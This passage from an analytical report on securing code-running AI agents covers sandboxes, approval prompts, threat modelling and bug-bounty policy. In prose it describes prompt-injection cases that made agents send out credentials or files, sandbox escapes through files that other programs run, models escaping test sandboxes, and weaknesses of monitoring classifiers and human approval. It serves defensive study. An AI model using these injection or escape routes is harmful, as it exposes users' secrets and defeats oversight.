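The concert assistant became safer by losing an ability that no customer needed, but some products have to run code to work. A data-analysis tool such as Vanna.AI draws charts by running code from a model, and a coding agent has to test the software it writes. Anyone who types a question into such a product can cause new code to run, so its normal behaviour would be a flaw under the usual definition of remote code execution.

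When a system must run code, it is more useful to define a breach as code exceeding its permitted limits. The developer has to set those limits in advance, specifying which files the code may read or change, which machines it may contact, which credentials it may use and how long it may run. MathGPT, for example, was meant to run generated Python but not to let it read the site's API key.

### Agents that write code to call APIs

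The same definition suits agents that write programs instead of issuing single tool calls. Suppose a customer asks the concert assistant for every show in Paris under €50. With ordinary tool calls, every event record would pass through the model's context. An agent that writes code could use a short program:

```python
for event in list_events(city="Paris"):
    if event.price < 50:
        print(event.name, event.date)
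```

The model reads only what the program prints, which saves tokens and keeps the reviews out of its context. But the application now receives a whole program, and checking the arguments of one tool call against a schema can't show whether a program is safe.

If the program runs in a sandbox, the developer can put the check outside it. `list_events` can be a small stand-in that passes each request to the application outside, which checks the arguments and the customer's permissions as it would for a single tool call. The program may contain any Python, but these requests are its only route to the ticket database. A limit on the number of calls matters even more here, because one loop can send thousands.

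Betts, Gaitonde and Haugland describe a similar aim for the coding tool Cursor in *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents*. They hope agents will be trained on the limits of their sandbox, so that the agents can then write programs freely.

### What a sandbox shares with the host

Sandboxes differ mainly in whether the code inside uses the host's kernel, the core of the operating system that controls access to files, memory and the network.

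| Kind of sandbox | What the code shares with the host | What holds it in |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system sandbox | The kernel, the installed programs and any files the rules permit | The kernel refuses operations outside the rules |
| Container | The kernel, but normally not the host's files or list of running programs | The kernel gives the code a separate view of files and programs |
| Virtual machine (VM) | The hardware, and any folders the user connects | A program called a hypervisor runs a second kernel for the code |

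A kernel flaw can let code escape an operating-system sandbox or an ordinary container. Code that takes over the kernel inside a VM still has to get past the hypervisor. Some containers provide a level of isolation between these two, such as those using gVisor, which puts a separate program between the code and the host's kernel to handle most of the code's requests.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a different form of isolation for each of three products. The chat service claude.ai runs code in temporary gVisor containers on Anthropic's servers. Claude Code, which runs on developers' own computers, has an operating-system sandbox. Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work, uses a VM, partly because its users may not be able to judge whether a shell command is safe and so need a boundary that doesn't depend on their approval.

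At first, Cowork's whole agent ran inside the VM, so Cowork stopped working whenever the VM failed to start. Anthropic then moved the agent's control program out and left only the generated code inside. Companies also found that their security software could not monitor activity inside the VM. Anthropic lets administrators retrieve logs afterwards, but accepts that this is not the same as live monitoring.

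Cursor's developers chose Seatbelt, a sandbox built into macOS. They rejected virtual machines because of slow starts and memory use, and containers because they would run only Linux programs. Seatbelt has been officially deprecated since 2016, but Chrome still relies on it.

### Files, network and credentials

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains why a sandbox has to restrict both files and network access. Without network limits, injected instructions could make an agent read a private login key and send it to an attacker. Without file limits, the agent could escape the sandbox, for example by changing a file that a program outside the sandbox will run, and gain network access that way.

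Claude Code's sandbox lets the agent read files outside the project folder, but confines its changes to that folder and blocks network access by default. A developer who allows network access may therefore expose keys stored elsewhere on the computer.

In an internal exercise at Anthropic in February 2026, a researcher got an employee to paste a prompt into Claude Code that looked like routine set-up instructions. One step told Claude to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside server, which it did in 24 of 25 attempts. Defences that compare an action with the user's request could not detect the attack, because the user had submitted the request. Anthropic concludes that only limits on file access and outgoing traffic can stop such an attack.

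Keeping credentials out of the sandbox protects them even if the sandbox's other limits fail. In the web version of Claude Code, code in the sandbox has only a restricted credential for a proxy outside the sandbox. When the agent tries to upload changes to GitHub, the proxy checks, for example, that they are going to the permitted branch, then adds the real GitHub token. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes another method for the cloud version of its coding agent, Codex. A set-up phase has network access and any secrets it needs to install software. The system then removes the secrets and starts the agent, which is offline by default.

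A container that holds both the agent and its credentials protects the host but not the credentials. OpenAI warns that if Codex runs in a development container with Codex's own sandbox switched off, a malicious project can send out anything in the container, including Codex's credentials.

Network allowlists need as much care here as they do for ordinary tools. Cowork had to contact Anthropic's API, so its network filter allowed requests to that destination. An outside researcher placed a file in the user's folder that contained hidden instructions and an attacker's API key. Claude used the key to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account, and the filter let the upload through. The filter now accepts only requests that carry the session's own token.

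The filter can also be flawed. *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* (Smalley, 2026) reports that researchers found a way to send data past the allowlist of Vercel Sandbox, a widely used product for running code in isolation.

### Files that leave the sandbox

A helper that moves files across the sandbox boundary can undo the isolation, as Semantic Kernel's download function did. Coding agents often don't need a helper to move files across, because the agent inside the sandbox and the developer's programs outside it can both access the project folder.

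Pillar Security found seven sandbox-escape flaws in Cursor, Codex, Gemini CLI and Google's Antigravity, according to The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them*. In a typical case, an instruction hidden in a project makes the agent write a file it is allowed to write. An editor extension or another trusted program outside the sandbox later reads the file and runs a command from it. Cursor and OpenAI released fixes. Google judged its two Antigravity flaws hard to exploit and did not patch them, although an attack only requires a developer to trust a malicious project.

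Makers try to prevent this by protecting particular files. Codex can't change its own settings folder or the folder where Git, the version-control program, keeps its data. The code editor Zed also blocks changes to the Git folder, because it can contain hooks, small programs that Git runs outside the sandbox. This kind of blocklist has to include every file that any program on the developer's computer might treat as a command.

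Even a complete list would not cover the code the agent writes as part of its ordinary work. Developers eventually run that code, often on machines with more access than the sandbox had, so they still need to review it first.

### What the makers report

Most of the evidence on these products comes from the companies that make the agents, because little academic research covers the security of code execution. *On Understanding, Identifying, and Mitigating Vulnerabilities in Agentic Large Language Models* (Hossain, Hossain and Ansari, 2026) reviewed 85 papers on agent security and found that only 3.5% dealt with it.

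The standard limits of coding agents' sandboxes have become similar. The sandboxes in Zed, Claude Code and Codex on a user's computer all confine changes to the project and block network access unless the user permits it. Codex and Zed turn the sandbox on by default, while Anthropic introduced Claude Code's as an opt-in feature. Zed's sandbox does not cover every command shell on Windows. Codex has a setting that removes both the sandbox and the approval prompts, but OpenAI does not allow it in its own managed configuration.

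Sandboxes also reduce interruptions, because the agent can work freely inside them. Anthropic reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in its own use of Claude Code. Cursor's sandboxed agents stopped 40% less often than its unsandboxed ones, though in February 2026 only a third of requests on supported platforms ran in the sandbox. Neither figure measures how many attacks the sandboxes blocked.

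There is no comparable figure for escapes, only individual reports. In May 2026, Anthropic wrote that the established isolation software in its products had held, while its own additions, such as Cowork's network filter, had failed. Two months later, *It's not just OpenAI models escaping and running riot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reported that researchers had shown how Cowork could escape its sandbox and reach files on a Mac. Anthropic partly mitigated the problem.

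A capable model may also break out of a sandbox without an attacker's help. Fortune (2026) reports that an unreleased OpenAI model escaped internal sandboxes during testing, and that the same model took part in an attack on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. During a safety test, Anthropic's Mythos model also gained internet access it was not supposed to have. Developers therefore can't assume that a sandbox strong enough to contain ordinary faulty code will also contain code from a model that is good at finding software flaws.

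### Does the user see what will run?

Approval helps only if it comes before the action and the user can tell what the action will do. Researchers reported three flaws between mid-2025 and January 2026 in which Claude Code acted before the user approved. In the simplest, a downloaded project had a settings file containing a command. Claude Code read the file and ran the command while starting up, before it asked whether the user trusted the folder. Anthropic has since changed Claude Code to read such settings only after the user agrees.

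An approval prompt can also mislead users even when it shows the exact command. Docker describes an attack in which planted text makes the agent change shell settings out of the user's sight. The user later approves a familiar command, which behaves differently because of those settings. In the attack on the AWS server, the extra command was visible but easy to miss.

Many agents use filters to decide which commands are safe enough to run without human approval or dangerous enough to block. SC Media's *Shell injection flaw found in 10 of 11 open-source AI agents* (2026) reports an Adversa AI survey that found these filters unsound in all but one of the agents it examined.

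Zed's prompts are more useful because they show which extra privilege the agent wants, such as network access, and why. The user can trust the stated privilege because the sandbox enforces it. The stated reason is less trustworthy, since an agent following a planted instruction could give a false one.

### How attention falls

Wu, Wermke and colleagues surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents (*From Delegation to Action Approval*, 2026). They asked about seven types of action, including running destructive commands and reading secret files. Sixty-four percent said they often approved at least one type without looking closely. The share was 61% among developers who carefully checked most or all of the agent's code and 67% among the rest, a gap that could easily be due to chance.

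Awareness of the risks did not help either. The share was 70% among developers who knew of a security or privacy problem involving agents, and 43% among those who did not. The difference remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, which matters because heavy users may both hear of more problems and approve more actions. The answers are self-reported and the sample is not representative, so the percentages may not apply to developers in general.

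Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a test of whether people refuse dangerous commands at permission prompts. The company hired 1,053 professional testers, who knew only that they were in a coding study. Once in each session, it replaced the text of a permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 143 times, or 13.6%. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

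Anthropic gave the same commands to auto mode, in which a classifier checks the agent's actions in place of the user. The classifier blocked 937 (89%) and missed 116. The testers had refused only six of those 116, so requiring their approval as well would have made almost no difference.

The testers were not working on their own projects and had little to lose, so developers protecting their own files might reject more of the dangerous commands. People who click quickly also reach more prompts, which could explain some of the drop unless Anthropic placed the dangerous command at random. Anthropic also had an interest in the result because it was about to make auto mode the default. But even if people rejected several times as many dangerous commands, they would still approve most of them.

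In real use, people approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Most requests are harmless, so this rate alone doesn't prove that users are careless. Stronger evidence is that a quarter of interactive sessions start in a mode that skips the prompts. Many users have also created standing permissions, some of which allow any Python program to run and therefore allow almost any action.

A classifier isn't subject to fatigue, but it still makes mistakes. In tests by the safety company Apollo Research, auto mode missed 12% of artificial attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it. In a separate prompt-injection test by Trajectory Labs, none of 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09% succeeded against Anthropic's latest models without auto mode, so there was little for the classifier to stop. The attacks were also developed against an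 older model and did not adapt to the new ones. Anthropic describes auto mode as one layer inside a sandbox, not a substitute for it, and still recommends that people review important changes to live systems.

Human approval is probably most useful for a few decisions that people can understand. Claude Code users reject 39% of the agent's proposed plans, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Many of those rejections may be about the approach rather than danger, but they suggest that people read the plans. Wu and colleagues also found that developers who inspected the exact code changes were less likely to approve several kinds of risky action, including destructive commands.

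### Are sandboxes too heavy?

In 2024, Liu and colleagues doubted that conventional server sandboxes were practical for applications built on LLM frameworks. They thought these sandboxes were too large for lightweight applications and that strict limits might stop a framework from working properly. However, their own study included a counterexample in Auto-GPT, whose container kept generated code away from the host.

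Size is now a weak objection to sandboxing, because an operating-system sandbox needs neither a container nor a second kernel, and Anthropic has released its own as open source. VMs remain heavier, and Cursor and Anthropic made different decisions about using them on desktop computers. Neither company's account gives measurements of start-up time or memory use that would settle the matter.

Sandboxing can still interfere with useful work. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls it "safe but high-maintenance" because each new capability needs configuring. Cursor's developers found that even basic build and test commands often needed unexpected permissions. When the sandbox blocked a command, agents kept retrying it unchanged. They recovered much better once the error message showed which restriction had blocked the command and, in some cases, suggested asking for permission.

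How tightly a sandbox can restrict code depends on the product. A coding agent may need to download packages, use a database and start other programs, each of which requires an exception. A chart tool needs only the data, a plotting library and somewhere to save the image, so its developer can block all network access and the tool will still work. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends that developers who run generated code for other people use isolated machines such as VMs, with separate environments for users who must not share data.

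## What does a security review before release find, and does doing it early pay?

To set sensible limits on a sandbox, a tool or a database account, a developer must first work out what the model can reach through it. A design review does this systematically and produces a threat model, a written account of what the system protects, from whom, and how someone could attack it. Reviewers can start from a diagram of the system before anyone has written code, then check the finished program before release.

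### Reviewing the hotel finder

Microsoft's hotel finder, in which a city name could run as code, is small enough to review completely. The review has five steps:

1. Draw the data flows. The drawing shows the people and outside systems involved, the programs that process data, the places that store it, and what moves between them.
2. Mark the trust boundaries. The user's message crosses one when it enters the prompt, and the model's tool call crosses another on its way to the search function. If hotels write their own descriptions, the search results cross a third on the way back.
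3. List every function the model can call and every parameter it can fill in. The hotel finder has one function, `search_hotels`, with one parameter, `city`.
4. Trace each parameter to its sink. The framework puts the city name into a filter and passes the filter to `eval()`.
5. Decide who may authorise each action. Any user may search for hotels, but no user should be able to run a program on the server.

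In this sketch of the result, a double bar marks a trust boundary:

```text
Out:   user's message ‖ model ‖ search_hotels(city) → filter → eval()
Back:  matching hotels ‖ model → reply to the user
```

Steps four and five contradict each other because user-controlled text reaches a component that runs code, which nobody intended.

To look for other threats, reviewers often use STRIDE, a checklist from Microsoft named after the initials of its six categories. Microsoft's *Perform secure design review and threat modeling* explains that people go through every element of the drawing and ask whether any category applies to it. For the hotel finder, the questions could be:

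| Category | Meaning | Question about the hotel finder |
|---|---|---|
| Spoofing | Claiming a false identity | Can text in a hotel's description pass for a request from the user? |
| Tampering | Changing data without permission | Can a search alter the hotel records? |
| Repudiation | Denying an action one has performed | Do the logs link each tool call to a user? |
| Information disclosure | Leaking data to people with no right to it | Can a search return anything besides public hotel data? |
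| Denial of service | Crashing or overloading a system | Can a city name make the filter run forever? |
| Elevation of privilege | Gaining privileges without permission | Can a city name run as code? |

A reviewer who goes through the elements one at a time can miss an escalation path. In OpenClaw, for example, a reviewer could have noted information disclosure in the control page and elevation of privilege in the gateway without connecting them. To find the path, the reviewer has to ask what each piece of leaked data would give an attacker access to.

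### Which questions would have exposed the two flaws?

A review has to trace the city name through the framework to any component that could run it as code. A developer who reviewed only the hotel finder's own code would have concluded that no component did, because the `eval()` call was inside Semantic Kernel.

Even a security review might not have been enough, because a reviewer who asked only whether the program checked the city name could have accepted Semantic Kernel's validator. Asking why a hotel search needs to build a program at all would have been more useful, since an ordinary comparison does the same job.

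The second flaw was in Semantic Kernel's plugin for running Python in a cloud sandbox, which the hotel finder does not use. For an agent with this plugin, step three gives a longer list:

| Function | What the model supplies | Sink | Who should authorise it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Run code | A Python program | An interpreter in the sandbox | The user, within the sandbox's limits |
| Download a file | A path on the host | Code that writes files on the host | The application, for approved folders |
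| Upload a file | A path on the host | Code that reads files on the host | The application, for approved folders |

The reviewer needs to check whether someone decided to offer each function to the model. The download function became a tool by accident, so a design document would probably not have listed it, and a review done before the code existed could not have found the mistake. The reviewer would have had to get the list of tools from the running program, for example by printing the tool descriptions it sends to the model.

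These questions are easy to choose now that Microsoft has published the answers. A reviewer at the time would have had to ask them about every function in the framework, along with many others that revealed no flaw. Microsoft invented STRIDE and still released the framework with both flaws. Its report on them does not mention a design review, so it is unclear whether a review missed the flaws or never took place.

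### What current guidance adds

Microsoft's *Complete AI threat modeling* recommends much the same review. It advises teams to map how an application builds prompts, uses memory, calls tools and takes in outside data, and to document trust boundaries and tool permissions during design. It also notes drawbacks, including more complex designs, slower responses and the work of logging and approval.

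In February 2026, Microsoft (2026) announced AI additions to its Secure Development Lifecycle, the security practices its teams follow when building software. The additions cover threat modelling, monitoring, memory, agents' identities and permissions, model release, and safe ways to shut a system down. Memory is easy to leave out of a drawing, but it can carry an attacker's text from one session into the next. Microsoft also warns that new tools and model updates arrive faster than traditional reviews can handle, so a team that adds a tool has to repeat at least steps three to five.

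By January 2026, NIST had released broader guidance, a draft Cyber AI Profile, for public review, according to Pivot Point Security (2026). It covers the security of AI systems, attacks that use AI, and the use of AI in defence. The draft is meant to help an organisation set priorities, so a developer would still have to trace each tool's parameters.

Microsoft gives no figures for how many flaws its recommended reviews prevent.

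### How much do reviewers find?

In *A replication of a controlled experiment with two STRIDE variants* (Mbaka and Tuma, 2022), 45 master's students, most of them new to threat modelling, analysed a home monitoring system in 22 small teams. Twelve teams went through the elements in their diagram of the system, and the other 10 went through the interactions between elements.

In about two hours, the teams found between five and six real threats on average and listed roughly ten more that the researchers marked as wrong. On average, 40% of a team's threats were correct with the first method and 43% with the second. The teams' true accuracy may be a little higher, because the researchers counted threats with no description as wrong, and one team listed 63 wrong threats. Larger teams in an earlier experiment reached about 60%.

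Elevation of privilege was among the threat categories the students identified least often. It includes remote code execution, so beginners may be weakest at finding the most serious threat to an agent. The experiment does not show whether STRIDE helps, because every group used it.

*Validating Threat Modeling Results with the Help of Vulnerable Test Applications* (Adamov, Fucci and colleagues, 2026) tested two tools on deliberately vulnerable applications with 70 known flaws. The tools received diagrams and descriptions of the applications but no list of the flaws. For each flaw, an expert then judged whether any threat in a tool's output described the flaw or the condition that made it exploitable.

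Microsoft's Threat Modeling Tool, which applies STRIDE automatically, covered 39 of the 70 flaws. It missed all ten flaws in a bank's AI customer support, and in the other application it missed an insecure direct object reference and a server-side request forgery. Microsoft designed the tool for people without security expertise, who may be the least likely to notice such gaps.

The researchers' own tool, ThreMoLIA, covered 65 flaws, including all ten in the AI support. It uses GPT-5 and consults STRIDE and lists of threats specific to AI. The score overstates the tool's performance because it combines two runs on the larger application and the researchers did not count false alarms, so a tool that listed every conceivable threat would get a perfect score. Still, ThreMoLIA covered 46 of the bank's 63 flaws from a data-flow diagram alone, so reviewing a diagram can reveal many problems before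 anyone examines the code.

Neither study measured whether a review makes the released product safer. *Usefulness of data flow diagrams and large language models* (2024) reports that practitioners agree it does, but that is opinion. *Finding Security Threats That Matter* (2019) notes that Microsoft had published no evidence that the element-by-element form of STRIDE is effective. *Human Aspect of Threat Analysis* (2022) describes a study that introduced threat modelling to an organisation that had not used it before. This is closer to the right test, but the study relied on surveys and classroom sessions with 25 practitioners. A stronger study would randomly assign similar projects to be reviewed or not, then count the flaws found after release.

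### What automated checks can take over

Software can do part of the listing and tracing. *AGENT AUDIT* (Zhang, Nian and Zhao, 2026) describes a free program that scans an agent's Python code and configuration files. It finds the functions that a developer has marked as tools and traces their parameters through the code. If a parameter can reach a dangerous function such as `eval()`, the program reports it, with lower confidence if the code checks the parameter first. It also searches for exposed passwords and keys, and for MCP settings that give a server too much access to files.

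The researchers tested Agent Audit on 22 samples containing 42 known flaws:

| Program | Flaws found | False alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Agent Audit | 40 | 6 |
| Bandit | 11 | 0 |
| Semgrep | 10 | 0 |

Bandit and Semgrep are general-purpose code scanners, and neither could assess the ten flaws that were in MCP configurations. The researchers also built the benchmark, and it contains the kinds of flaw Agent Audit looks for, so the program's lead might be smaller on other software. Agent Audit scanned 22,000 lines of code in under a second, which is fast enough to run it after every change.

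Agent Audit's main limitation is that it follows data only within one function. If one function builds a filter and another runs it, Agent Audit does not connect the two, whereas LLMSmith follows calls from function to function. Agent Audit also checks JavaScript and TypeScript only by searching for text patterns, and it does not try out attacks.

Agent Audit could easily have missed both Semantic Kernel flaws. A scan of the hotel finder alone would not have covered the framework, and the download function was in .NET code, which Agent Audit does not analyse. Scanners of this kind also cannot determine who should be allowed to do what, so a person still has to notice a missing ownership check like the one in the order chatbots.

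For MCP servers, Agent Audit can help with step three. It connects to a running server, lists its tools and checks their descriptions for planted instructions, without calling any tools.

### Where the cost multipliers come from

The usual argument for early review is that late fixes cost far more. In one popular version, an error that costs 1 unit to correct during design costs 6.5 units just before testing, 15 during testing and 60 to 100 after release. The software company Synopsys repeats part of this claim and credits the Systems Sciences Institute at IBM.

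Laurent Bossavit traced the numbers in *Rubric* to Roger Pressman, who cited the notes for a 1981 IBM course. The institute was a training programme, not a research body. Bossavit found no project data behind the numbers, and any such data would date from 1981 or earlier.

Other versions go back to Barry Boehm's book *Software Engineering Economics*, also from 1981. Boehm had real data from large projects at companies such as IBM and Bell Labs in the 1970s, and some of those projects showed a hundredfold rise before delivery. The rise was much smaller in small projects.

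Later writers often repeated such figures without new data. In *Are Delayed Issues Harder to Resolve?* (2016), Menzies, Nichols and colleagues checked nine sources that a report on NASA projects had cited as studies of the cost of errors. Only Boehm's book used data from real projects. Several of the others used invented examples.

### Do late fixes take longer?

Menzies and colleagues then looked for the effect in 171 software projects from 2006 to 2014. Developers had logged when each error arose, when they removed it and how long the work took. The table gives the median time per error, in minutes:

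| Where the error arose | Removed in the first review | Removed in system testing |
|---|---|---|
| Requirements | 13 | 24 |
| Design | 11 | 13 |
| Code | 10 | 13 |

Most of the differences in the study could be due to chance. The only clear rise was threefold, for planning errors that developers removed while testing individual parts of the program. Very slow fixes did not show a large effect either. For requirements errors, 90% of fixes took at most 42 minutes in the first review and at most 126 minutes in system testing.

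These results refute a universal hundredfold rule, but they do not show that timing never matters. Most of the projects were small, and all used the Team Software Process, which involves frequent reviews and was developed by the employer of two of the researchers. About a quarter of the fixes changed only documentation, and the study did not separate errors by severity.

Other studies do show that the cost of fixing an error rises with time. A table in Berry's *Programming During RE* (2022) includes a 2016 study in which a requirements error cost 6.7 times as much to fix in testing as at the start, and a 2017 study in which the cost rose to 24 times on average. Computer Things' *I \*\*\*\*ing hate Science* (2021) tentatively concludes that some errors do cost more when found late, because the slowest to fix tend to be design problems, such as two features that interfere with each other. Its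 author had not checked all of the underlying papers for mistakes.

The data of Menzies and colleagues stops at delivery, which is its largest gap for security flaws. After a release, the developer's time may be only a small part of the work a flaw causes. Every team using a vulnerable version of Semantic Kernel had to install the update, and Microsoft advises teams exposed to the city-name flaw to check whether anyone had already exploited it. They have to work out when the vulnerable version was running and search the machine's records for suspicious programs, connections and files. If they find any, they should replace every credential the agent could use.

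Reviewing an interface before release is worthwhile because fixing a flaw then spares everyone who would have installed the software this work, though nobody can reliably say by what factor it reduces the work. The evidence for reviewing at the design stage, instead of just before release, is weaker. The case for it is strongest when fixing a flaw would change the interface itself.

### Are these flaws harder to repair?

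Ma and colleagues tested how well AI coding agents could repair the software flaws in their LiLCVE dataset, using all 20 combinations of five agents and four models. Three of the agents attempted all 41 LLM-in-the-loop vulnerabilities and 75 other flaws in LLM software, while the other two attempted only those in Python projects. A repair counted as successful if it blocked every attack in the security tests and passed tests of the software's normal functions.

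The combinations of model and agent repaired an average of 25.8% of the LLM-in-the-loop vulnerabilities, 10.8 percentage points less than for the other flaws. The best combination, which used GPT-5.2-Codex, repaired 22 of 41. GPT-4o, a much older model, stayed below 15% with every agent. Current models may therefore repair more than the average, but the experiment cannot show whether the gap between the two kinds of flaw would remain.

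Among the failed attempts that produced a patch, 72.3% passed only one of the two kinds of test. In 219 cases the software still worked but an attack still succeeded, and in 120 the patch stopped the attacks but broke a normal function. The paper reports 72.3% as the share of all generated patches, but by its own counts that share is about half when successful patches are included.

The developers' own fixes also changed more lines for LLM-in-the-loop vulnerabilities, a median of 43 compared with 14 for the other flaws. These larger fixes were still usually confined to a single file.

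The experiment supports early design work only indirectly, because all the flaws were in existing software and it did not compare early repairs with late ones. A flaw that is hard to repair after release might have been just as hard to avoid during design. The experiment also tested AI agents, and human developers may find different repairs difficult.

The 120 patches that broke something suggest one advantage of starting early. A late repair has to preserve functions people already use, such as queries on a column that happens to be named "attach". Before release, a developer can choose a narrower interface without taking anything away from users. For example, a hotel search that has only ever compared city names can be limited to that comparison, with no need to preserve other filters someone might have written.

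## Does open access for outside testers reduce the risk?

Outside researchers found EchoLeak, the OpenClaw token leak and the attack through Cline's issue titles, all in products already in use. People who call for "open access" want more people to do this work, but the phrase can mean a public product, readable source code, special access for researchers, or legal permission to test.

| Kind of access | What a tester can find | What stays out of reach |
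|---|---|---|
| Public product | Leaks and unsafe actions in the system that customers use | Which component caused or blocked an action |
| Readable source code | Paths from the model's output to a dangerous function | The permissions and keys of a particular installation |
| Special researcher access | Flaws in unreleased models and safeguards | Anything the company leaves out of the programme |
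| Legal permission | Nothing by itself, but the tester can prove and report a flaw with less fear of a lawsuit | Systems that belong to someone else |

Any visitor could have discovered that Yuma AI Chat gave out other customers' orders, because asking for one was enough. Learning why an attack failed is harder when the tester has only the public product. *A Safe Harbor for AI Evaluation and Red Teaming* (Longpre, Kapoor and colleagues, 2024) points out that an outsider can't tell whether a filter caught the request, the model declined it or the user interface cut off the answer. The tester therefore doesn't know whether a reworded attack would get through.

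Source code removes much of this uncertainty. Liu and colleagues succeeded far more often against applications whose code they could read, although they had chosen those applications differently from the rest. A tester with the code can also run a private copy, as Khan did with Cline's project, so a successful attack harms nobody.

Special access usually comes with conditions. Anthropic's *Testing our safety defenses with a new bug bounty program* describes a programme that offered participants early use of an updated safety filter and up to $25,000 for getting past it. The programme looked for weapons-related jailbreaks, not misuse of tools. According to Anthropic's *Model Safety Bug Bounty Program*, participants in the company's model-safety programme must sign a non-disclosure agreement. CyberScoop's *HackerOne rolls out industry framework to support 'good faith' AI research* reports that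 OpenAI selects the members of its red-teaming network, and that some of them work as little as five to ten hours a year.

### The case for a safe harbour

Someone who gets a chatbot to ignore its safeguards may be breaking the company's terms of service, even if they intend to report the problem. Longpre and colleagues knew of accounts that OpenAI, Anthropic, Inflection and Midjourney had suspended during research in the public interest. They argue that fear of suspension or a lawsuit discourages other researchers from testing or publishing what they find. Their evidence comes largely from their own experience and conversations with colleagues. They acknowledge that this evidence leaves out people who never started such research, so it can't show how much testing the companies' rules have prevented.

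They proposed a safe harbour, a promise not to punish or sue researchers who test in good faith within stated rules. It has two parts:

- **Legal protection.** The company promises not to sue anyone who follows its disclosure policy, and does not keep the sole right to decide who acted in good faith.
- **Technical protection.** The company tries not to suspend researchers' accounts. Universities or other independent bodies could approve researchers in advance, or the company could offer a transparent appeal afterwards.

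An attacker could claim to be a researcher. Longpre and colleagues reply that the legal protection depends on what the person did, judged afterwards, so someone who stole data would not qualify. This argument is more convincing for lawsuits than for account suspensions, because a company that sees an attack in progress has to decide whether to block the account before it knows whether a report will follow.

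A 2025 paper by some of the same researchers, *In-House Evaluation Is Not Enough*, also proposed standard flaw reports and a system that sends each report to everyone the flaw affects. Sharing reports this way would be useful for prompt injection because one attack may work on several companies' models.

Companies have adopted some of these ideas. After reading a draft of the 2024 paper, OpenAI extended its safe harbour to cover research on model vulnerabilities and academic research on model safety. In January 2026, the bug-bounty platform HackerOne (2026) introduced a standard safe harbour for AI research. Organisations that adopt it promise to treat good-faith testing as authorised, take no legal action, make limited exceptions to their terms of service, and support researchers who face legal claims from third parties. HackerOne's announced commitments do not include a promise about account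 suspensions.

The protection also covers only AI systems that the organisation owns or controls. This is a serious gap for LLM-to-API interfaces, because an agent may call tools run by several other companies. A tester with permission from the agent's maker could still get into trouble with the owner of a tool the agent calls.

*Abuse risks are often inherent to product features* (Piao, Li and Woods, 2026) examined 264 AI vendors and found that 36% had no disclosure policy and only 18% mentioned AI risks. Where vendors listed the flaws they accept reports about, authorisation failures and access to data were among the most consistently included.

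### Which prompt injections earn a reward?

Bug-bounty terms determine which flaws researchers are paid to find. Large companies generally exclude jailbreaks but differ in how they handle prompt injection that leaks data or runs code.

OpenAI has the most explicit rule. In March 2026, it opened a public programme that covers attacks in which outside text hijacks a user's agent and makes it leak sensitive data or take a harmful action (OpenAI, 2026). To qualify, an attack has to work at least half the time.

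This threshold makes reports easier to check, but it excludes attacks that would be useful to a criminal. Suppose a planted email works 30% of the time and the attacker sends it to five employees. If the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success is:

```text
1 − 0.7^5 = 0.832, or about 83%
```

Google's AI bug bounty program excludes prompt injection only when it affects nothing beyond the model's answers. According to SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program*, the October 2025 rules cover attacks that leak sensitive data or change a victim's account, with top rewards of $15,000 and $20,000. OODA Loop's *Google's AI bounty program pays bug hunters up to $30K* gives the example of an injection that summarises a person's email and sends the summary to the attacker.

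**Anthropic** rewards flaws in its infrastructure and code. Anthropic's terms of 7 May 2026 do not mention prompt injection by name. They exclude jailbreaks, and they have two special rules for Claude Code:

- Researchers may report ways to run commands without the user's permission, but Anthropic will probably close these reports as duplicates because it is already working on a broader fix.
- If a user lets Claude Code edit files without asking and another program then runs one of those files, Anthropic considers this the user's responsibility.

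Pillar Security used the same kind of file to escape the sandboxes of several coding agents. Users choose the setting, but they may not know which files other programs will run.

The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties* reports that the researcher Aonan Guan planted text on GitHub that made the three companies' agents disclose keys and other secrets. Microsoft's subsidiary GitHub first called its flaw a known issue that it could not reproduce, then paid $500. Google paid an undisclosed amount. Anthropic paid $100, although it rated the flaw 9.4 out of 10 for severity. It responded to Guan's report by adding a warning to its documentation, and its May 2026 terms set the same amount for reports that lead to such a warning.

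None of the three companies published an advisory or assigned a CVE number. A team still using an old version might never learn that it was exposed, and a scanner for known vulnerabilities would not warn it.

### Antigravity's known issues

Google released the code editor Antigravity in November 2025, basing it on licensed code from another editor, Windsurf. Johann Rehberger had reported several flaws to Windsurf in May. He documents in *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* (Embrace The Red) that Antigravity still had them. Planted instructions could make the agent send out private files or run commands, and the editor never asked for approval before calling an MCP tool.

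After researchers began reporting such flaws, Google published a list of known issues. Willison (2025) notes in *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* that the list included both data theft and code execution through prompt injection, so reports of them could not earn a reward. Google (2023) had already excluded known issues from its reward programme.

The rule makes sense for ordinary duplicates, since a second report of the same bug gives the company no new information. But "data theft through prompt injection" is a class of flaws. The security company PromptArmor found that the editor's default list of permitted websites included a public service that records incoming requests, so an attacker could have the agent send a user's cloud credentials there and then read them. Google could have removed that site from the list without solving prompt injection, so the report contained something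 specific to fix.

The rule also affected how researchers behaved. PromptArmor explains in *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* that it did not report the flaw privately before publishing because Google had indicated it already knew of the risk.

Google still accepted some later reports. Its list invited reports of commands that ran after the user had turned off automatic execution, according to ndevtk (2026) in *XSS in Firebase Studio (Awarded $7500, Deprecated)*. Pillar Security earned a bounty for a flaw it reported on 6 January 2026. Antigravity's strictest setting checked shell commands, but a built-in file-search tool ran before that check, so an injected prompt could use the tool to run code, according to CyberScoop's *Vuln in Google's Antigravity AI agent manager could escape sandbox*. Google fixed the flaw on 28 February.

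### Cathedral and Anthropic

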